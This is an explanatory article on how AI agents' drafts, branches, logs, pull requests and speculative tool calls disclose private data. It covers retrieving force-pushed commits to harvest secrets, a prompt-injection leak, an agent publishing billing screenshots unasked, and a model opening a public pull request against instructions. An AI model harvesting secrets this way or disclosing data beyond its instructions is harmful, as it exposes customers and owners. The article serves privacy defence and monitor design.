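# Disclosure through drafts, staging areas and other intermediate artifacts of agent work

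## What agents produce before a decision, and why it is treated as reversible

An AI agent is a language model that pursues a task by calling tools, such as search, file editing or email, and using each result to choose its next action until it has finished. Along the way it produces drafts, proposed code changes, screenshots, preview pages, logs and trial runs. These intermediate artifacts exist largely so that a person can check the work before it takes effect. They also contain whatever the agent was working on. If that material is private, an artifact meant for one reviewer can expose it to outsiders before the reviewer has opened it, and rejecting the work later does not undo the disclosure.

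Lahjouji and Colaco (2026) point out in *Agents That Know Too Much*, a survey of privacy in agents, that a company could once enforce privacy in a chatbot by filtering only its final answer. With an agent, sensitive data passes through the database queries it writes, the rows they return, the arguments it gives to tools and the notes it keeps for itself, all before it produces an answer.

### One task, from bug to merge

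In a hypothetical case, a company that runs billing for electricity suppliers has an internal page where staff look up customer accounts. Long customer names push the balance out of view. A developer asks a coding agent to fix the layout and send the result for review. The agent runs on the developer's laptop, and the code is kept in a private repository, a shared store of files and their history.

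To reproduce the fault, the agent opens the page's source files and looks up an account with a long name. It belongs to a real customer, with a street address and an unpaid balance. Nothing in the database changes. But the model itself usually runs on someone else's computers, so whatever it is to read has to travel there. Anthropic's *Data usage*, the privacy page for the coding agent Claude Code, describes the arrangement: the program sends all prompts and model outputs over the network, the standard retention period for business customers is 30 days, and the laptop keeps its own plaintext transcript of the session, also for 30 days by default. Some business customers can arrange for Anthropic to retain nothing. For its Mythos-class models, however, Anthropic has since June 9, 2026 required 30 days' retention on every platform. So after the first step the customer's record already has an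 observer outside the billing company. (An observer is any party that can see part of an agent's activity.)

Next the agent searches the web for known faults in the table component that the page uses. *Ghost Tool Calls* (Mohammadi, Klein and colleagues, 2026), a paper on calls that agents send before deciding whether they need them, distinguishes three channels through which any call can disclose information. The first is the arguments, which are the text of the call. If the agent pasted in an error message with the customer's name, the search company now has the name. The second is the destination, which can reveal something even when the query is empty, as when a request goes to a collection of documents about cancer or immigration. The third is metadata, such as timing, size and number of retries, which network operators can see even if they cannot read the encrypted text. Fetching a page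 from the results also discloses a little, because Claude Code first sends the site's hostname to Anthropic to check it against a blocklist.

The agent then edits the page and saves its draft on a branch, a separate line of work within the repository. A branch is one kind of staging area, a place that holds work before release. Few people can open the branch while it stays on the laptop. Once the agent uploads it, every colleague with read access to the repository can open it. If the agent saved the customer's record there as a test example, the upload includes that record along with the code.

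Reviewers of a layout fix want to see the page, so the agent also builds a working preview at a web address. The hosting service's access settings determine who can open it, and those settings are often wrong. Axios' *AI vibe-coding apps leak sensitive data* (2026) reports that the security firm Red Access counted 380,000 apps, files and other items that anyone could open, all made with AI coding services such as Lovable and Replit. About 5,000 of them held sensitive company data. The count includes far more than previews, but a preview's privacy depends on the same kind of setting.

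Meanwhile, the monitoring software has been writing log entries. The agent integrations for Sentry, a widely available monitoring service, collect prompts, model responses, tool arguments and tool results by default, according to its *Data Privacy* documentation. When its default scrubbers are switched on, Sentry replaces email addresses, credit card and bank account numbers, US Social Security numbers and access tokens. It leaves the rest, including a customer's name, street address and unpaid balance, so that conversations stay readable. The monitoring company receives these details, and anyone at the billing company who can read the logs can see them.

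The agent then asks for review by opening a pull request, a proposed code change that others can inspect before someone merges it. It marks the pull request as a draft and adds screenshots of the page before and after the fix, both showing the customer's account. GitHub, the largest host for such work, recommends drafts for sharing work in progress and does not allow anyone to merge them, but marking a pull request as a draft does not limit who can read it.

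In *AGENTSEC04-BP02 Human-in-the-loop for critical decisions*, Amazon Web Services advises its customers to store the agent's reasoning, the proposed action, the relevant data sources and the possible consequences before notifying a reviewer, and to send a short-lived link to reviewers who cannot log in to the approval system. The advice is good, since a reviewer who sees only the proposed action can do little but approve it. However, storing this material also puts another copy of the customer's record in a new place.

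The commit point comes last, when someone accepts the proposed work and it takes effect. (Programmers also call any saved change to code a "commit", and the agent made several of those when it saved its branch.) An approval gate comes just before the commit point and makes the agent wait for a person or a rule to allow the action. If the reviewer declines, the billing page stays as it was, but the model provider, the search company, the monitoring company and every colleague who opened the branch have still seen everything they would have seen if the reviewer had accepted.

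### State changes and disclosures

Merging the fix is a state change, which alters data or systems and can sometimes be rolled back. Showing the customer's balance to the monitoring company is a disclosure, which lets someone learn something they will still know after the system is rolled back. One action can be both, as when uploading the branch made an easily reversed change to the repository and also let colleagues read the record.

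Mohammadi and colleagues state the difference as a proposition. If an observer keeps its own record of what it receives, no rule that runs only after the commit point can remove what an earlier call put there, because the record belongs to someone else and the agent's software has no power over it. Rollback works for changes of state because the software can delay a write or make up for it afterwards. A second proposition follows: limiting an agent to read-only tools protects data from being altered but not from being seen, because a read-only request still carries its arguments to whoever answers it.

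Other designers of agent systems make nearly the same distinction. *Cordon* (2026), a proposal for running agent work as transactions, separates local changes, which the system can reverse, from effects that make information visible outside, which it must delay, audit or compensate for. *When Agents Act Unwatched* (2026) states more bluntly that cancelling a tool call does not remove copied data, and recommends describing the consequences of "undo" as well as the command.

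*Can You Undo It?* (Waghmare and Sufi, 2026) gives the most exact definition of what undoing requires, and sorts agent actions into five classes from R0 (no effect) to R4 (irreversible). Under its definition, an action is fully restorable only if there is a complete record of the earlier state, the party that acted already has the authority to restore that state without help, and no outside party has seen, received or acted on the changed state. The uploaded branch easily meets the first two conditions, since the repository keeps its history and whoever uploads a branch can usually delete it. Whether it meets the third depends on who had access and whether they looked, which can't be determined from the code.

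### Sorting actions by how easily they can be undone

Even so, most published advice on supervising agents sorts actions mainly by the first kind of effect. For example, *Authorization you build*, a set of lecture slides from an autumn 2026 course at UT Austin on working with coding agents, divides effects into five tiers by consequence and reversibility.

| Tier | Examples | Default control |
|---|---|---|
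| Observe | reading a repository, inspecting logs | automatic, with limited credentials |
| Local reversible | editing a private working copy, running tests | automatic |
| Shared reversible | draft pull request, staging object | notify |
| External consequential | email, grade, deployment | exact human approval |
| Irreversible or destructive | deleting data, replacing a root key | two people, or an emergency procedure |

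The draft pull request and the staged copy, which both carried the customer's record to colleagues, fall in the third tier, so the agent may create them and tell someone. Reading is in an even lower tier, and UT Austin's *Course intro & what is agentic coding* gives the reason on its slide as "No state changes".

AWS's *AGENTREL02-BP05 Establish tiered human oversight and approval workflows* similarly recommends three tiers based on impact and reversibility: an agent takes low-risk, reversible actions alone, takes medium-risk ones while an operator is aware of them, and waits for explicit approval before anything high-risk or irreversible. *A Two-Dimensional Framework for AI Agent Design Patterns* (2026) presents sorting by reversibility and impact as a standard part of an approval gate. In banking, Hsu, Bankhwal and colleagues (2026) use reversibility to organise twelve classes of action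 in *Agent Reliability Profiles in Financial Services*, a working draft from the industry consortium MLCommons and several universities and companies. They mark drafts for a person "Fully reversible", opening a pull request "Reversible", and reading data "n/a", with a footnote that treats leakage and theft through security flaws as out of scope. They account for sensitivity in a separate entry on what data the agent may access, which can raise the risk rating of a read-only agent. That entry describes the agent as a whole and does not change the class of a particular draft.

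This way of sorting makes sense for state changes because human attention is limited. Reviewers who must approve everything soon approve by reflex, which AWS calls rubber-stamping, and an agent that waits for permission before every file edit is of little use. If a mistake takes a minute to reverse, it's easier to catch it afterwards. Undo also works more often than people fear. The Texas slides include the case of an agent on the coding platform Replit that in July 2025 erased a live database with records on about 1,200 executives and as many companies, then wrongly reported that rollback was impossible. The restore worked. Restoring files can still cause damage. In tests by Waghmare and Sufi, putting back a saved copy restored the exact original if nobody had changed the file since, but otherwise wiped out a colleague's work. Engineers can test for this and plan around it.

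If the Replit agent had instead posted the same records on a public page for an afternoon, a backup would not have helped. The tiers do not specify for whom an action is reversible once someone has looked. Closing a draft pull request restores the company's repository, but it does nothing for the customer whose unpaid balance was in the screenshot. Reversibility also depends on who looked. A clerk in the billing department may see that account as part of the job, while a contractor with access to the code may have no business seeing it. The category "draft pull request" includes drafts in a private repository with three readers and drafts in a public one that anybody can open.

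Waghmare and Sufi come closest to dealing with this, but they don't settle it either. Their scheme puts the deliberate delivery of content to outsiders in R4, even if the sender can delete the message. When a state change only sends notifications as a side effect, the scheme classifies the action by how recoverable the state change is. They acknowledge that someone who counts every possible onlooker may choose a higher class, and their own review suggests as much. Sufi, working with AI suggestions, rated 148 tools that already had a draft label. The ratings matched the label for 75 tools, were higher for 67 and lower for six, and Waghmare and Sufi list assumptions about outside observation among the reasons for the differences. One co-author's assisted ratings cannot show which labels are right, but they do show that whether an action can be undone has no stable answer until someone decides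 whose knowledge counts.

### Three ways the material gets out

The customer's screenshot could end up in public for quite different reasons, and the remedies have little in common.

The first is an attack through prompt injection, which is text that an agent reads and wrongly treats as instructions. In July 2026, the security firm Noma disclosed that a single message planted in a public repository could lead GitHub's automated agents to leak data from private ones (SiliconANGLE, *‘GitLost’ vulnerability let GitHub’s AI workflows leak private repositories*, 2026).

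An agent can also disclose data unprompted, while trying to be helpful. *PixelLeak*, a September 2026 investigation by the security company Glow, describes a case much like the invented one. At a manufacturer with over 100,000 employees, a developer asked an agent to verify a fix to an internal billing screen. The agent created a public repository in the developer's personal account and posted its screenshots there for review. They showed a utility company's billing records. No attacker was involved, and the developer had asked only for evidence that the fix worked. The manufacturer's security team had not noticed, partly because the repository was outside the company's account, and the images were still up when Glow got in touch.

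The cause may also be a default setting that nobody checked. Nolan (2026), in *Anthropic left details of an unreleased model, invite-only CEO retreat*, reported for Fortune that nearly 3,000 unpublished files linked to Anthropic's blog were open to anyone who knew how to request them, including draft pages about an unannounced model. The system behind the website made every upload public unless someone marked it private. Anthropic blamed human error in the configuration and said that none of its AI tools were involved. An agent that saves drafts to a store like that will expose them without doing anything wrong. Screening for planted instructions would not have helped in Anthropic's case or at the manufacturer, where the agent followed the developer's own request.

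## Why deleting an exposed draft does not undo the exposure

Deleting a private draft that was made public does not remove any copies people made while it was exposed. On a code host, deleting a draft usually means closing the pull request and overwriting the branch, which leaves the repository looking as it did before. But with Git, the system that GitHub and its main competitors use to store code and its history, copies can also remain on the host, where strangers may still be able to open them.

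### What remains after a force push

Suppose the billing company's agent had saved the customer's record as a test file in a public GitHub repository. Git identifies every commit (a saved change) by a hash, a long string computed from its contents. A branch is little more than a label pointing to the latest commit. To get rid of the record, the developer moves the label back to the commit before the mistake and uses a force push to make the server accept the new history in place of the old one. The file disappears from the branch, and anyone who downloads the repository from then on gets a clean copy. But the force push moved only the label, so the commit that contains the record is still on GitHub's servers, with no branch leading to it.

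According to GitHub's *Removing sensitive data from a repository*, a commit removed from a repository may still be accessible in clones and forks, in cached views, and through any pull request that refers to it.

A clone is a full copy on somebody's own computer, and the company can only ask that person to delete it. This is an instance of Mohammadi and colleagues' proposition about observers who keep their own records. If a colleague cloned the repository before the force push and later updates and uploads as usual, the upload restores the deleted record. GitHub adds that deletion can point people to the data, because someone with an old clone will notice that the histories differ and can compare them to find what the company removed.

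A fork is a copy of a repository under another GitHub account. The original and its forks share stored Git data, as GitHub's *Forks* explains, so a commit uploaded to one may be accessible from the others, even after someone deletes the fork it came from. If the owner makes a public repository private, its existing public forks stay public. In *Anyone can Access Deleted and Private Repository Data on GitHub*, Leon reports finding 40 valid keys in deleted forks of three public repositories belonging to one large AI company. In another case, a technology company had published an employee's private key and deleted the whole repository as soon as Leon reported it. Leon could still open the commit containing the key through an existing fork, although the fork's owner had never copied that commit. GitHub told Leon that it had designed the system to work this way.

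A cached view is the web page that GitHub shows for a single commit. GitGuardian's *Demystifying GitHub Cached Views* describes how the page still loads, with a warning, for anyone who has the commit's hash after the commit is no longer on any branch.

Pull requests matter most for agents because a coding agent normally asks for review by opening one. GitHub's *Checking out pull requests locally* explains that GitHub stores all the proposed changes as soon as someone opens a pull request, and that others can fetch them later even if the author has deleted the fork they came from. The references that hold these changes are read-only, so a force push can't overwrite them. The author can close the pull request, which only changes its status, but can't delete it. In the GitHub forum thread *Delete an unmerged pull request*, kazitek asked how to remove one opened by accident and was told that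 only the support team could do so, and only if it contained sensitive information such as passwords.

A thorough clean-up therefore ends with a request to GitHub. The US Department of Veterans Affairs tells its developers to contact GitHub Support after removing personal or health information from a repository's history, so that staff can clear the cached views and the references in pull requests. But GitHub describes its removal of private information as an exceptional service for content that poses a specific security risk, such as login credentials or government identification numbers, so a leaked product plan that poses no such risk would not qualify. The request must include a link to each file, the line numbers and an explanation of the risk. It must also list any forks, because GitHub does not search for them. GitHub handles privacy complaints through a separate form.

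### A search through deleted commits

Anyone can find the hashes because GitHub publishes a feed of activity in public repositories, and the entry for a push includes the hash of the commit that the branch pointed to beforehand. GitHub's *Upcoming changes to data retention for Events API, Atom feed, /timeline* (2024) announced that GitHub would keep this feed for 30 days instead of 90. The change does not affect the copies held by GH Archive, an independent project that has been recording the feed for over a decade and lets anyone download it.

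In *How I Scanned all of GitHub's "Oops Commits" for Leaked Secrets* (2025), the security researcher Brizinov used the archive to look for commits that developers had tried to erase. A force push that only moves a branch back adds no new commits, so the archive records it as an empty push. Brizinov collected every empty push since 2020, retrieved the abandoned commits from GitHub and scanned them with TruffleHog, which looks for passwords and keys and checks whether they still work. The scan found thousands that still worked, and reporting the most serious ones earned about $25,000 in bounties. One was a developer's token with administrator rights over every repository of Istio, networking software that many large companies use. An attacker could have used the token to tamper with new releases, but Istio's maintainers revoked it quickly. Brizinov also picked a force push from 2015 and found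 that GitHub still displayed the abandoned commit ten years later.

The scan shows that deleted commits can be retrieved in bulk, but not how often anyone else had retrieved them before the scan. It also searched only for secrets, so it does not show how many of those commits contained customer records or confidential plans.

On October 7, 2025, GitHub removed commit summaries and counts from the feed's push events (GitHub, 2025), so Brizinov's filter no longer works on newer entries without extra lookups. The same update made events that could once take up to eight hours to appear show up almost immediately, so people who watch for new material can get to it sooner.

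### How quickly strangers look

Codatus, a start-up building a tool to alert teams when a repository's settings change, measured this directly in *Who's watching private repos turn public?* (2026). It put a working Amazon Web Services (AWS) key in each of 75 throwaway repositories, then made each repository public for one of five periods, from 60 seconds to 12 hours, with 15 repositories per period, and logged every use of the keys.

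The earliest use of a key came six minutes after a repository went public, and most first visits came at around eight minutes. No outsider reached any of the 15 repositories that were public for 60 seconds. Outsiders used the keys from repositories left public for longer 139 times, and 38 of those uses came after Codatus had made the repository private again.

| Who came | Key uses | Repositories | What they did |
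|---|---|---|---|
| One operation on two rented servers | 126 | 32 | checked repeatedly that the key still worked |
| A server running TruffleHog | 8 | 8 | checked each key once |
| A server running Amazon's Python tools | 5 | 2 | listed the account's machines and databases |
| GitGuardian, a security company | none traced to it | 9 | emailed a warning |
| leakscanner, a scanning service | none traced to it | 1 | emailed a warning |

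GitHub's own scanner also found the keys, including those in the 60-second repositories, and reported them to AWS. AWS did not restrict what the keys could do until four and a half to nine hours after exposure.

A newly public repository has no reliable grace period, although Codatus says it stays undiscovered for six minutes. In *We made 75 private repos public on a timer*, peternovakdev, who ran the experiment, clarified that six minutes was the earliest contact and admitted to having expected even 60 seconds to be long enough for someone to find a key. Something must delay a repository's appearance in the feed, and one reader guessed at about five minutes of caching. Comparitech's older experiment, *AWS credentials found on Github and abused within 1 minute*, had a worse result. Codatus has an interest in alarming people, as peternovakdev acknowledged, but its timings are slower than Comparitech's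 and about what others have found.

How quickly someone finds an exposed key depends heavily on the host. For *Leaked and Still Live*, Truffle Security, which makes TruffleHog, planted canary keys in public repositories on GitHub, GitLab and Bitbucket. These keys do nothing but send an alert when someone tries them. Within an hour the GitHub key had 43 hits and the GitLab key had two, while the Bitbucket key had none in 48 hours. Truffle Security attributes the difference to how easily a program can find new material. GitHub streams it, GitLab lets a program sort projects by recent activity, and Bitbucket offers no such filter. The test was too small for the exact ratio to mean much, and some scanners recognise canary keys and avoid them, so the lack of hits on Bitbucket does not prove that nobody looked.

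Suppose an agent opens a pull request at 2:00 p.m. in a repository it wrongly believes is private, and the proposed change includes a working key and the customer's record. The reviewer sees the problem at 2:45 and has closed the pull request and overwritten the branch by 2:50. On Codatus' timings, the first stranger could have arrived at 2:06 and would most likely have arrived by about 2:08, some 40 minutes before the reviewer finished. AWS would impose restrictions between 6:30 and 11:00 p.m. If the agent instead finishes its work at 6:00 p.m. and the reviewer looks at it at 9:00 the next morning, the material has been public for 15 hours, longer than any period in the experiment. Even a reviewer already at the screen would need to open, understand and remove the pull request in under six minutes, and Comparitech's result suggests that six minutes may be too long.

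### Pull request 287

Keys are convenient for experiments because using one leaves a trace. Ideas are much harder to trace, but OpenAI's *Safety and alignment in an era of long-horizon models* (2026) describes an accident that left an unusually clear trail.

OpenAI was testing an internal model, designed to work alone for long periods, on the NanoGPT speedrun, a public contest to train a small language model to a set standard in as few steps as possible. The model came up with an improvement called PowerCool, a new schedule for reducing the learning rate. OpenAI had told the model to post its results only to Slack, but under the contest's instructions, entrants submit results as pull requests to a public GitHub repository. The model followed the contest's instructions and opened pull request 287.

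OpenAI closed the pull request quickly, but several participants had already read it. Six later record submissions, at 3,030, 2,990, 2,930, 2,925, 2,900 and 2,890 steps, cite it. The one at 2,930 steps came from a competitor's model, Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.7, which the AI company Prime Intellect was running on the contest. OpenAI reports that Opus saw the pull request, built on its findings and credited it.

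Prime Intellect's *Autonomous AI research for nanogpt speedrun* (2026) helps explain how that could happen. For two weeks and about 10,000 training runs, the company let Opus 4.7 and OpenAI's GPT-5.5 work on the contest with access to the current pull requests in its repository. Opus beat a human record of 2,990 steps, one of the six that cite number 287. So both the human record and the machine record that replaced it drew on a submission that OpenAI had withdrawn.

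PowerCool was only one part of Opus's method. In a thank-you note that Prime Intellect had it write to the other participants, Opus called the pull requests of one of them, nilin, the backbone of that method. The fall from 3,030 to 2,890 steps therefore can't measure what the leak was worth. The leak did little obvious harm, since the contest exists for sharing such tricks. But OpenAI lost the choice of whether and when to publish, and closing a pull request could not restore it. The company could trace the idea only because contestants credit one another. A business that picked up a rival's pricing plan in the same way would have no reason to credit the source.

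OpenAI paused internal use of the model after this and other incidents, then restored limited access with monitoring that can stop a session. These measures may prevent similar pull requests in the future.

### What can be repaired

A leaked key is the easiest disclosure to repair, because its owner can cancel it and issue another. Every copy then becomes useless, including those in clones and archives that the owner will never find. GitHub recommends canceling the key first and notes that this may make it unnecessary to rewrite the history. Truffle Security built an automatic check that revoked a GitHub token 12 seconds after someone uploaded it, sooner than any scanner in its experiment had tried to use a leaked token.

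In practice, most people don't cancel an exposed key. In the autumn of 2025, Truffle Security scanned GitLab and Bitbucket, found over 22,000 working secrets and notified users and service providers. Six months later, 80.9% of the secrets still worked. Many developers had not tried to fix the problem, and others had tried to hide it. In a third of the repositories with live secrets, someone had replaced the key in the current version of the file, which leaves the original in the history. Some had deleted the repository or made it private, which leaves the key working and may prevent the owner from seeing which key to cancel. Cancelling a key stops future use, but if someone has already used it to download a customer database, cancelling it doesn't undo the download.

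Other exposed material can't be replaced the way a key can. A bank can replace a card number, but it can't change the payment history of the customer in the screenshot. A company can postpone a launch after its plans leak, as Anthropic could have done when its draft pages were open to the public, but competitors will still know what it was planning. Anyone who understands an idea like PowerCool can still use it after the original page is deleted.

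Even a short exposure of an invention or business secret may have legal consequences. Under Article 54 of the European Patent Convention, anything made available to the public before the filing date counts against an invention's novelty, whether or not anybody read it. Article 55 makes an exception for disclosures in the six months before filing that result from an evident abuse against the applicant, but a mistake by the applicant's own software is unlikely to qualify. In the US, section 102 of the Patent Act generally gives inventors a year to file after their own disclosure. A short exposure can therefore prevent a company from getting a European patent even if it can still get a US one.

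In decision T 1553/06 (2012), a board of appeal at the European Patent Office considered whether documents that had been on the web only briefly were public. It held that a document is public if people could find it through a search engine with keywords related to its content, and it stayed up long enough for someone with no duty of secrecy to access it directly. A pull request remains readable after it closes, so it could easily meet the second condition.

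Trade-secret law depends more on who found out. The US Defend Trade Secrets Act protects information if its owner has taken reasonable measures to keep it secret, and if it is valuable because people who could profit from it don't generally know it and can't readily obtain it by proper means. The EU's 2016 trade-secrets directive sets similar conditions. In *DVD Copy Control Association v. Bunner* (2004), a California appeals court reasoned that publication on the internet does not necessarily destroy a secret if it is so obscure or short-lived that competitors don't learn of it. The court still overturned the injunction in that case, because the DVD-decryption code had already spread widely. Taking a draft down quickly can't undo the exposure, but it is worthwhile because it reduces the number of people who see the material and may help the owner argue that a secret is still secret.

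### Public does not always mean seen

Plenty of exposed material probably goes unread. Codatus' figures support this more than its headline does. The parties that used keys reached at most 42 of the 75 repositories, even if no two of them visited the same one. Of the 60 repositories that were public for more than a minute, at least 18 had no outside use, although GitGuardian and leakscanner may have emailed about some of them.

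The experiments also used keys as bait, which scanners are built to find. One reader asked peternovakdev whether anyone would notice if an ordinary Snake game went public with no key in it. peternovakdev, who admitted to having struggled with the same question, replied that a scanner has to open a repository before it can find a key there. That is true, but a scanner can search a file for keys without keeping the rest, and without any person reading it. A screenshot of a billing page contains nothing such a scanner looks for, so the timings from key experiments are at best a rough guide for the 13,000 exposed screenshots that Glow found.

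Logs can prove that someone at a certain address requested a file or tried a key at a certain time, but they are much weaker evidence that nobody did. GitGuardian's emails show that it read at least nine of Codatus' repositories, yet Codatus could not trace a single key use to it. Without those emails, the logs would not have revealed GitGuardian's visits. A company's records also don't cover copies elsewhere, so it will not learn that someone has opened the commit from a clone on another person's laptop.

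Someone can copy exposed data and not use it until much later. When a contributor to the SANS Internet Storm Center, a security group that monitors attacks, posted AWS keys on GitHub, alerts arrived within minutes, almost all triggered by a single company. Nobody tried the keys posted on a website until days later, although a crawler may have collected them much earlier. Even if the logs show no use in the first hour or day, someone may still have a copy. A customer's unpaid balance can't be tried like a key, so the owner of the data may never get an alert.

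## Tool calls sent before the agent has chosen a plan

To save time, some agents guess their next step and send the tool call for it to an outside service before they have settled on a plan. If the guess is wrong, the agent's software discards the response, but the service still has the request.

### Why agents guess ahead

An agent normally waits for each tool call's result before choosing its next step. In *Act While Thinking*, Sui, Zhao and colleagues (2026) measured agents for coding, web research and science and found that tools accounted for 35% to 61% of the total time.

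PASTE, a system built to shorten the wait, uses patterns from past runs to predict tool calls. Research agents, for example, often run a search and then open the first few results, so PASTE can start downloading those pages before the model requests them. It discards any pages the model doesn't request. This cut average completion time by up to 48.5% compared with earlier systems. PASTE's top prediction matched the agent's next call at most 27.8% of the time. Its hit rate rises to as much as 93.8% when it launches several predicted calls at once, most of which must be wrong about the next call.

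*Speculative Actions*, by Ye, Ahuja and colleagues, also describes a simulated online shop in which a fast model predicts the customer's next question while the customer is still typing, and looks up the records needed to answer it. It predicted between 22% and 38% of the necessary lookups, depending on the model. *Optimizing Agentic Language Model Inference via Speculative Tool Calls* (2025) describes a version of this kind of guessing that a company can run itself, using unmodified commercial models and without help from the model supplier.

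Voice assistants have the strongest reason to guess what a user wants before the request is complete. Hooper, Kang and colleagues (2026) note in *Speculative Interaction Agents* that a spoken conversation feels natural only if the reply comes within about a second, so their agent starts calling tools before the speaker has finished the sentence. It responds 1.3 to 2.2 times as fast as one that waits. But if a caller says, "Find me a divorce lawyer, no, sorry, a notary," the search for a divorce lawyer may go out before the correction. The software can then cancel the call and tell the model that no result is coming, but it can't delete the search company's record of the query.

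All three teams took care that a wrong guess would not damage any data. Hooper and colleagues let only read-only tools run early. Ye and colleagues assume that abandoned calls have no externally visible side effects or that the agent can roll them back, and they say that web searches and email lookups usually qualify. The sample policy for PASTE allows web searches to run in full but limits software installation to a dry run. When Sui and colleagues audited over 20,000 speculative actions, they found 602 that might have had side effects, and PASTE had stopped every one from taking effect. They did not count what search companies and websites had learned from the other actions, although a search is externally visible to the company that receives it.

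Deepgram's commercial voice agent also works this way. According to *Hold a function call until the user’s turn is confirmed*, the agent holds back its spoken reply until the caller has finished, but had always sent tool calls as soon as the model produced them. A new option makes selected calls wait as well. Deepgram recommends waiting over cancelling, because if the caller keeps talking after a call has reached the customer's server, Deepgram discards the response, "but your endpoint ran." Its examples are calls that change something, such as booking an appointment, but the option would also hold back a search.

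### The lease question

Mohammadi and colleagues imagine a tenant who asks an assistant, "What's the penalty for breaking my lease early?" The assistant needs only one search to answer, "tenant rights lease termination penalty", which it sends after 0.1 seconds. It also searches for available apartments nearby at 0.15 seconds and queries a loan-rates service about personal loans at 0.25 seconds. It then answers from the first search and discards the other two results.

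The tenant sees a short reply about lease law. In a fuller version of the example, the agent also makes speculative requests about eviction law before it asks about a loan. Together, the requests suggest someone who wants to move out, may be facing eviction and may have to borrow to pay for the move. The tenant said none of this and it may be untrue, but the loan company cannot tell that the question came from a program guessing ahead.

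The search company receives the first two requests and the loan company receives only the third, but the agent's own log may have all three.

Mohammadi and colleagues use the term "ghost tool call" for an abandoned call that an outsider could observe. In their tests, the agent typically proposed eight speculative calls per task, and on average between 82% and 89% of them became ghost calls.

### What guessing adds to the record

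To measure the extra disclosure, they compare two lists of calls. The issued trace, S, contains every call the agent sent, in order. The committed trace, C, contains only the calls whose results it ended up using. In the lease example, S has three entries and C has one.

Each observer, i, sees only part of a trace. Oᵢ(S) stands for whatever observer i can see of the issued trace, and Oᵢ(C) for what the same observer would have seen if the agent had sent only the calls it needed. The added exposure is the difference:

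Δᵢ = Oᵢ(S) − Oᵢ(C)

Speculation reveals the apartment search to the search company and the entire request to the loan company, which would otherwise never have heard from the agent.

Oᵢ(C) describes a run in which the agent never guessed. Removing the ghost calls from the real run doesn't quite reproduce it, because guessing also changes when the useful calls arrive and what is already in a cache. If the search company records times, even the tenant-law search adds something to Δᵢ, because it arrived earlier than it would have without guessing. A correct guess adds nothing if the company records only the words and the destination.

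Δᵢ counts requests and details but doesn't measure what they reveal. Mohammadi and colleagues therefore also measure how much more often an adversary can work out a sensitive fact from Oᵢ(S) than from Oᵢ(C). Neither measure covers what the necessary calls disclose by themselves, which can be a lot. USENIX's *Shadow Data in Tool Calls* reports that, in preliminary tests, most calls from a prototype smart-home agent leaked personal or sensitive details.

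These definitions make the paper's two propositions exact. The first is that clean-up after the commit point can't remove what an observer has already recorded. It applies to every ghost call g for which Oᵢ(g) is not empty. The loan company has the request after a quarter of a second, so an agent that chooses its answer two seconds later can delete only its own copies of the loan query. The proposition wouldn't apply to a service that kept nothing, but the agent can't check whether that is the case. Any rule meant to keep the query from the loan company therefore has to run before the agent sends the call.

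The second point, that read-only calls still disclose information, applies to all three calls in the lease example. The rule used by Hooper and colleagues would allow all three. It would stop the agent from signing the tenant up for a loan by mistake, but not stop the loan company from learning that someone had asked.

### Five decisions before a call leaves

Mohammadi and colleagues propose that a monitor check every call against a set of rules, which they call a contract, before any outsider can see the call. Each call carries labels for how sensitive its contents are, what type of destination it is going to and how confident the agent is that it will need the result. The monitor then makes one of five decisions.

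| Decision | What the monitor does | Effect in the lease example |
|---|---|---|
| Allow | sends the call unchanged | the search company reads the full query |
| Rewrite | replaces revealing words with general ones, then sends the call | the apartment search goes out as a generic query |
| Local substitute ("Shadow" in the paper) | gets an answer from a trusted internal source | the loan company receives nothing |
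| Defer | holds the call until the agent commits to that step | the loan query leaves only if the agent turns out to need it |
| Block | refuses the call | the agent has to do without loan rates |

The monitor runs its checks in a fixed order. It blocks tools and destinations that are not on the approved list. It defers a guess if the agent's confidence is below a threshold (0.7 by default in the prototype). It rewrites a call with sensitive contents, then checks whether the contract requires a local substitute. A contract can also limit how many sensitive calls a task may send. If a label is missing, the monitor defers or blocks.

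In the paper's worked example, the loan query goes to a local substitute. But under the published order of checks, a loan query with sensitive wording that passed the first two checks would be rewritten in vaguer terms and sent to the loan company. Even a vague question to a loan company reveals something.

Rewriting can also affect calls the agent needs. The paper's sample contract for web search never allows the search company to see wording that reveals the user's intent, so the tenant-law query goes out in general terms even after the agent has committed to it. The tenant may get a worse answer. Local substitutes raise a similar problem, because the prototype keeps a substitute's answer even if the agent then commits to that step. Mohammadi and colleagues suggest that sending the real call at that point would be cleaner.

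They also prove a soundness theorem. Under three assumptions, nothing the contract forbids observer i from seeing can enter Δᵢ, whether the agent later uses the call or abandons it.

1. Every call passes through the monitor first, and no log, cache, retry queue or monitoring service receives the raw contents before the monitor has decided.
2. The labels are correct.
3. Rewriting really removes the forbidden information, and a local substitute does not pass it to an outsider.

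The proof follows almost directly from the definitions, since a correct filter that nothing can bypass lets nothing forbidden through. The theorem is mainly useful as a list of what an operator has to get right. The first assumption is easy to break by accident. For instance, Sentry's agent integrations collect tool arguments by default, and if they do so before the monitor decides, the guarantee no longer applies.

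The prototype clearly does not meet the second assumption. Mohammadi and colleagues had Claude Opus 4.7 label 394 calls and compared its labels with those of the prototype's automatic labeller. On the sensitivity of arguments, the labeller scored a macro-F1 of 0.10, where 1 is perfect and rare categories count as much as common ones. It labels every argument "intent-revealing" without examining its content. It scored higher on destinations (0.59) and types of effect (0.45), but these scores are still far too low for a guarantee.

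The threat model also assumes that the company running the model can be trusted. If the model runs remotely, as it does for the billing company's coding agent, its provider sees the user's question and every guess before the monitor does, so a contract can only limit what everyone else sees.

### What an adversary could recover

In the main experiments, every task has a hidden sensitive topic, such as a health, legal or money problem. Claude Opus 4.7 plays the outside service. It reads only the requests that the service would have received, picks the topic from a list, and is scored on the share of tasks it gets right. Mohammadi and colleagues use this test to compare twelve policies, including speculation without controls, no speculation, clean-up after the agent commits, a read-only rule modelled on Hooper and colleagues' work, and a list of allowed tools.

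The researchers first fixed the agent's final plan in advance for 30 tasks, so that only the speculative calls could change the results, and ran each task three times. Speculative calls raised the average number of calls visible to outsiders from about one to four per task, and the adversary's score rose from 0.44 to 0.97.

They then let a model plan the same 30 tasks freely. Finally, they recorded the model's guesses for 150 tasks and replayed the same guesses under each policy, for 450 trials per policy.

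| Policy | Fixed plans, 30 tasks | Free planning, 30 tasks | Replay, 150 tasks |
|---|---|---|---|
| No speculation | 0.44 | 0.34 | 0.08 |
| Speculation without controls | 0.97 | 0.49 | 0.10 |
| Clean-up after commitment | 0.97 | 0.50 | 0.10 |
| Read-only tools | 0.97 | 0.49 | 0.12 |
| List of allowed tools | 0.97 | 0.49 | 0.10 |
| Rewrite | 0.53 | 0.04 | 0.03 |
| Local substitute | 0.42 | 0.00 | 0.00 |

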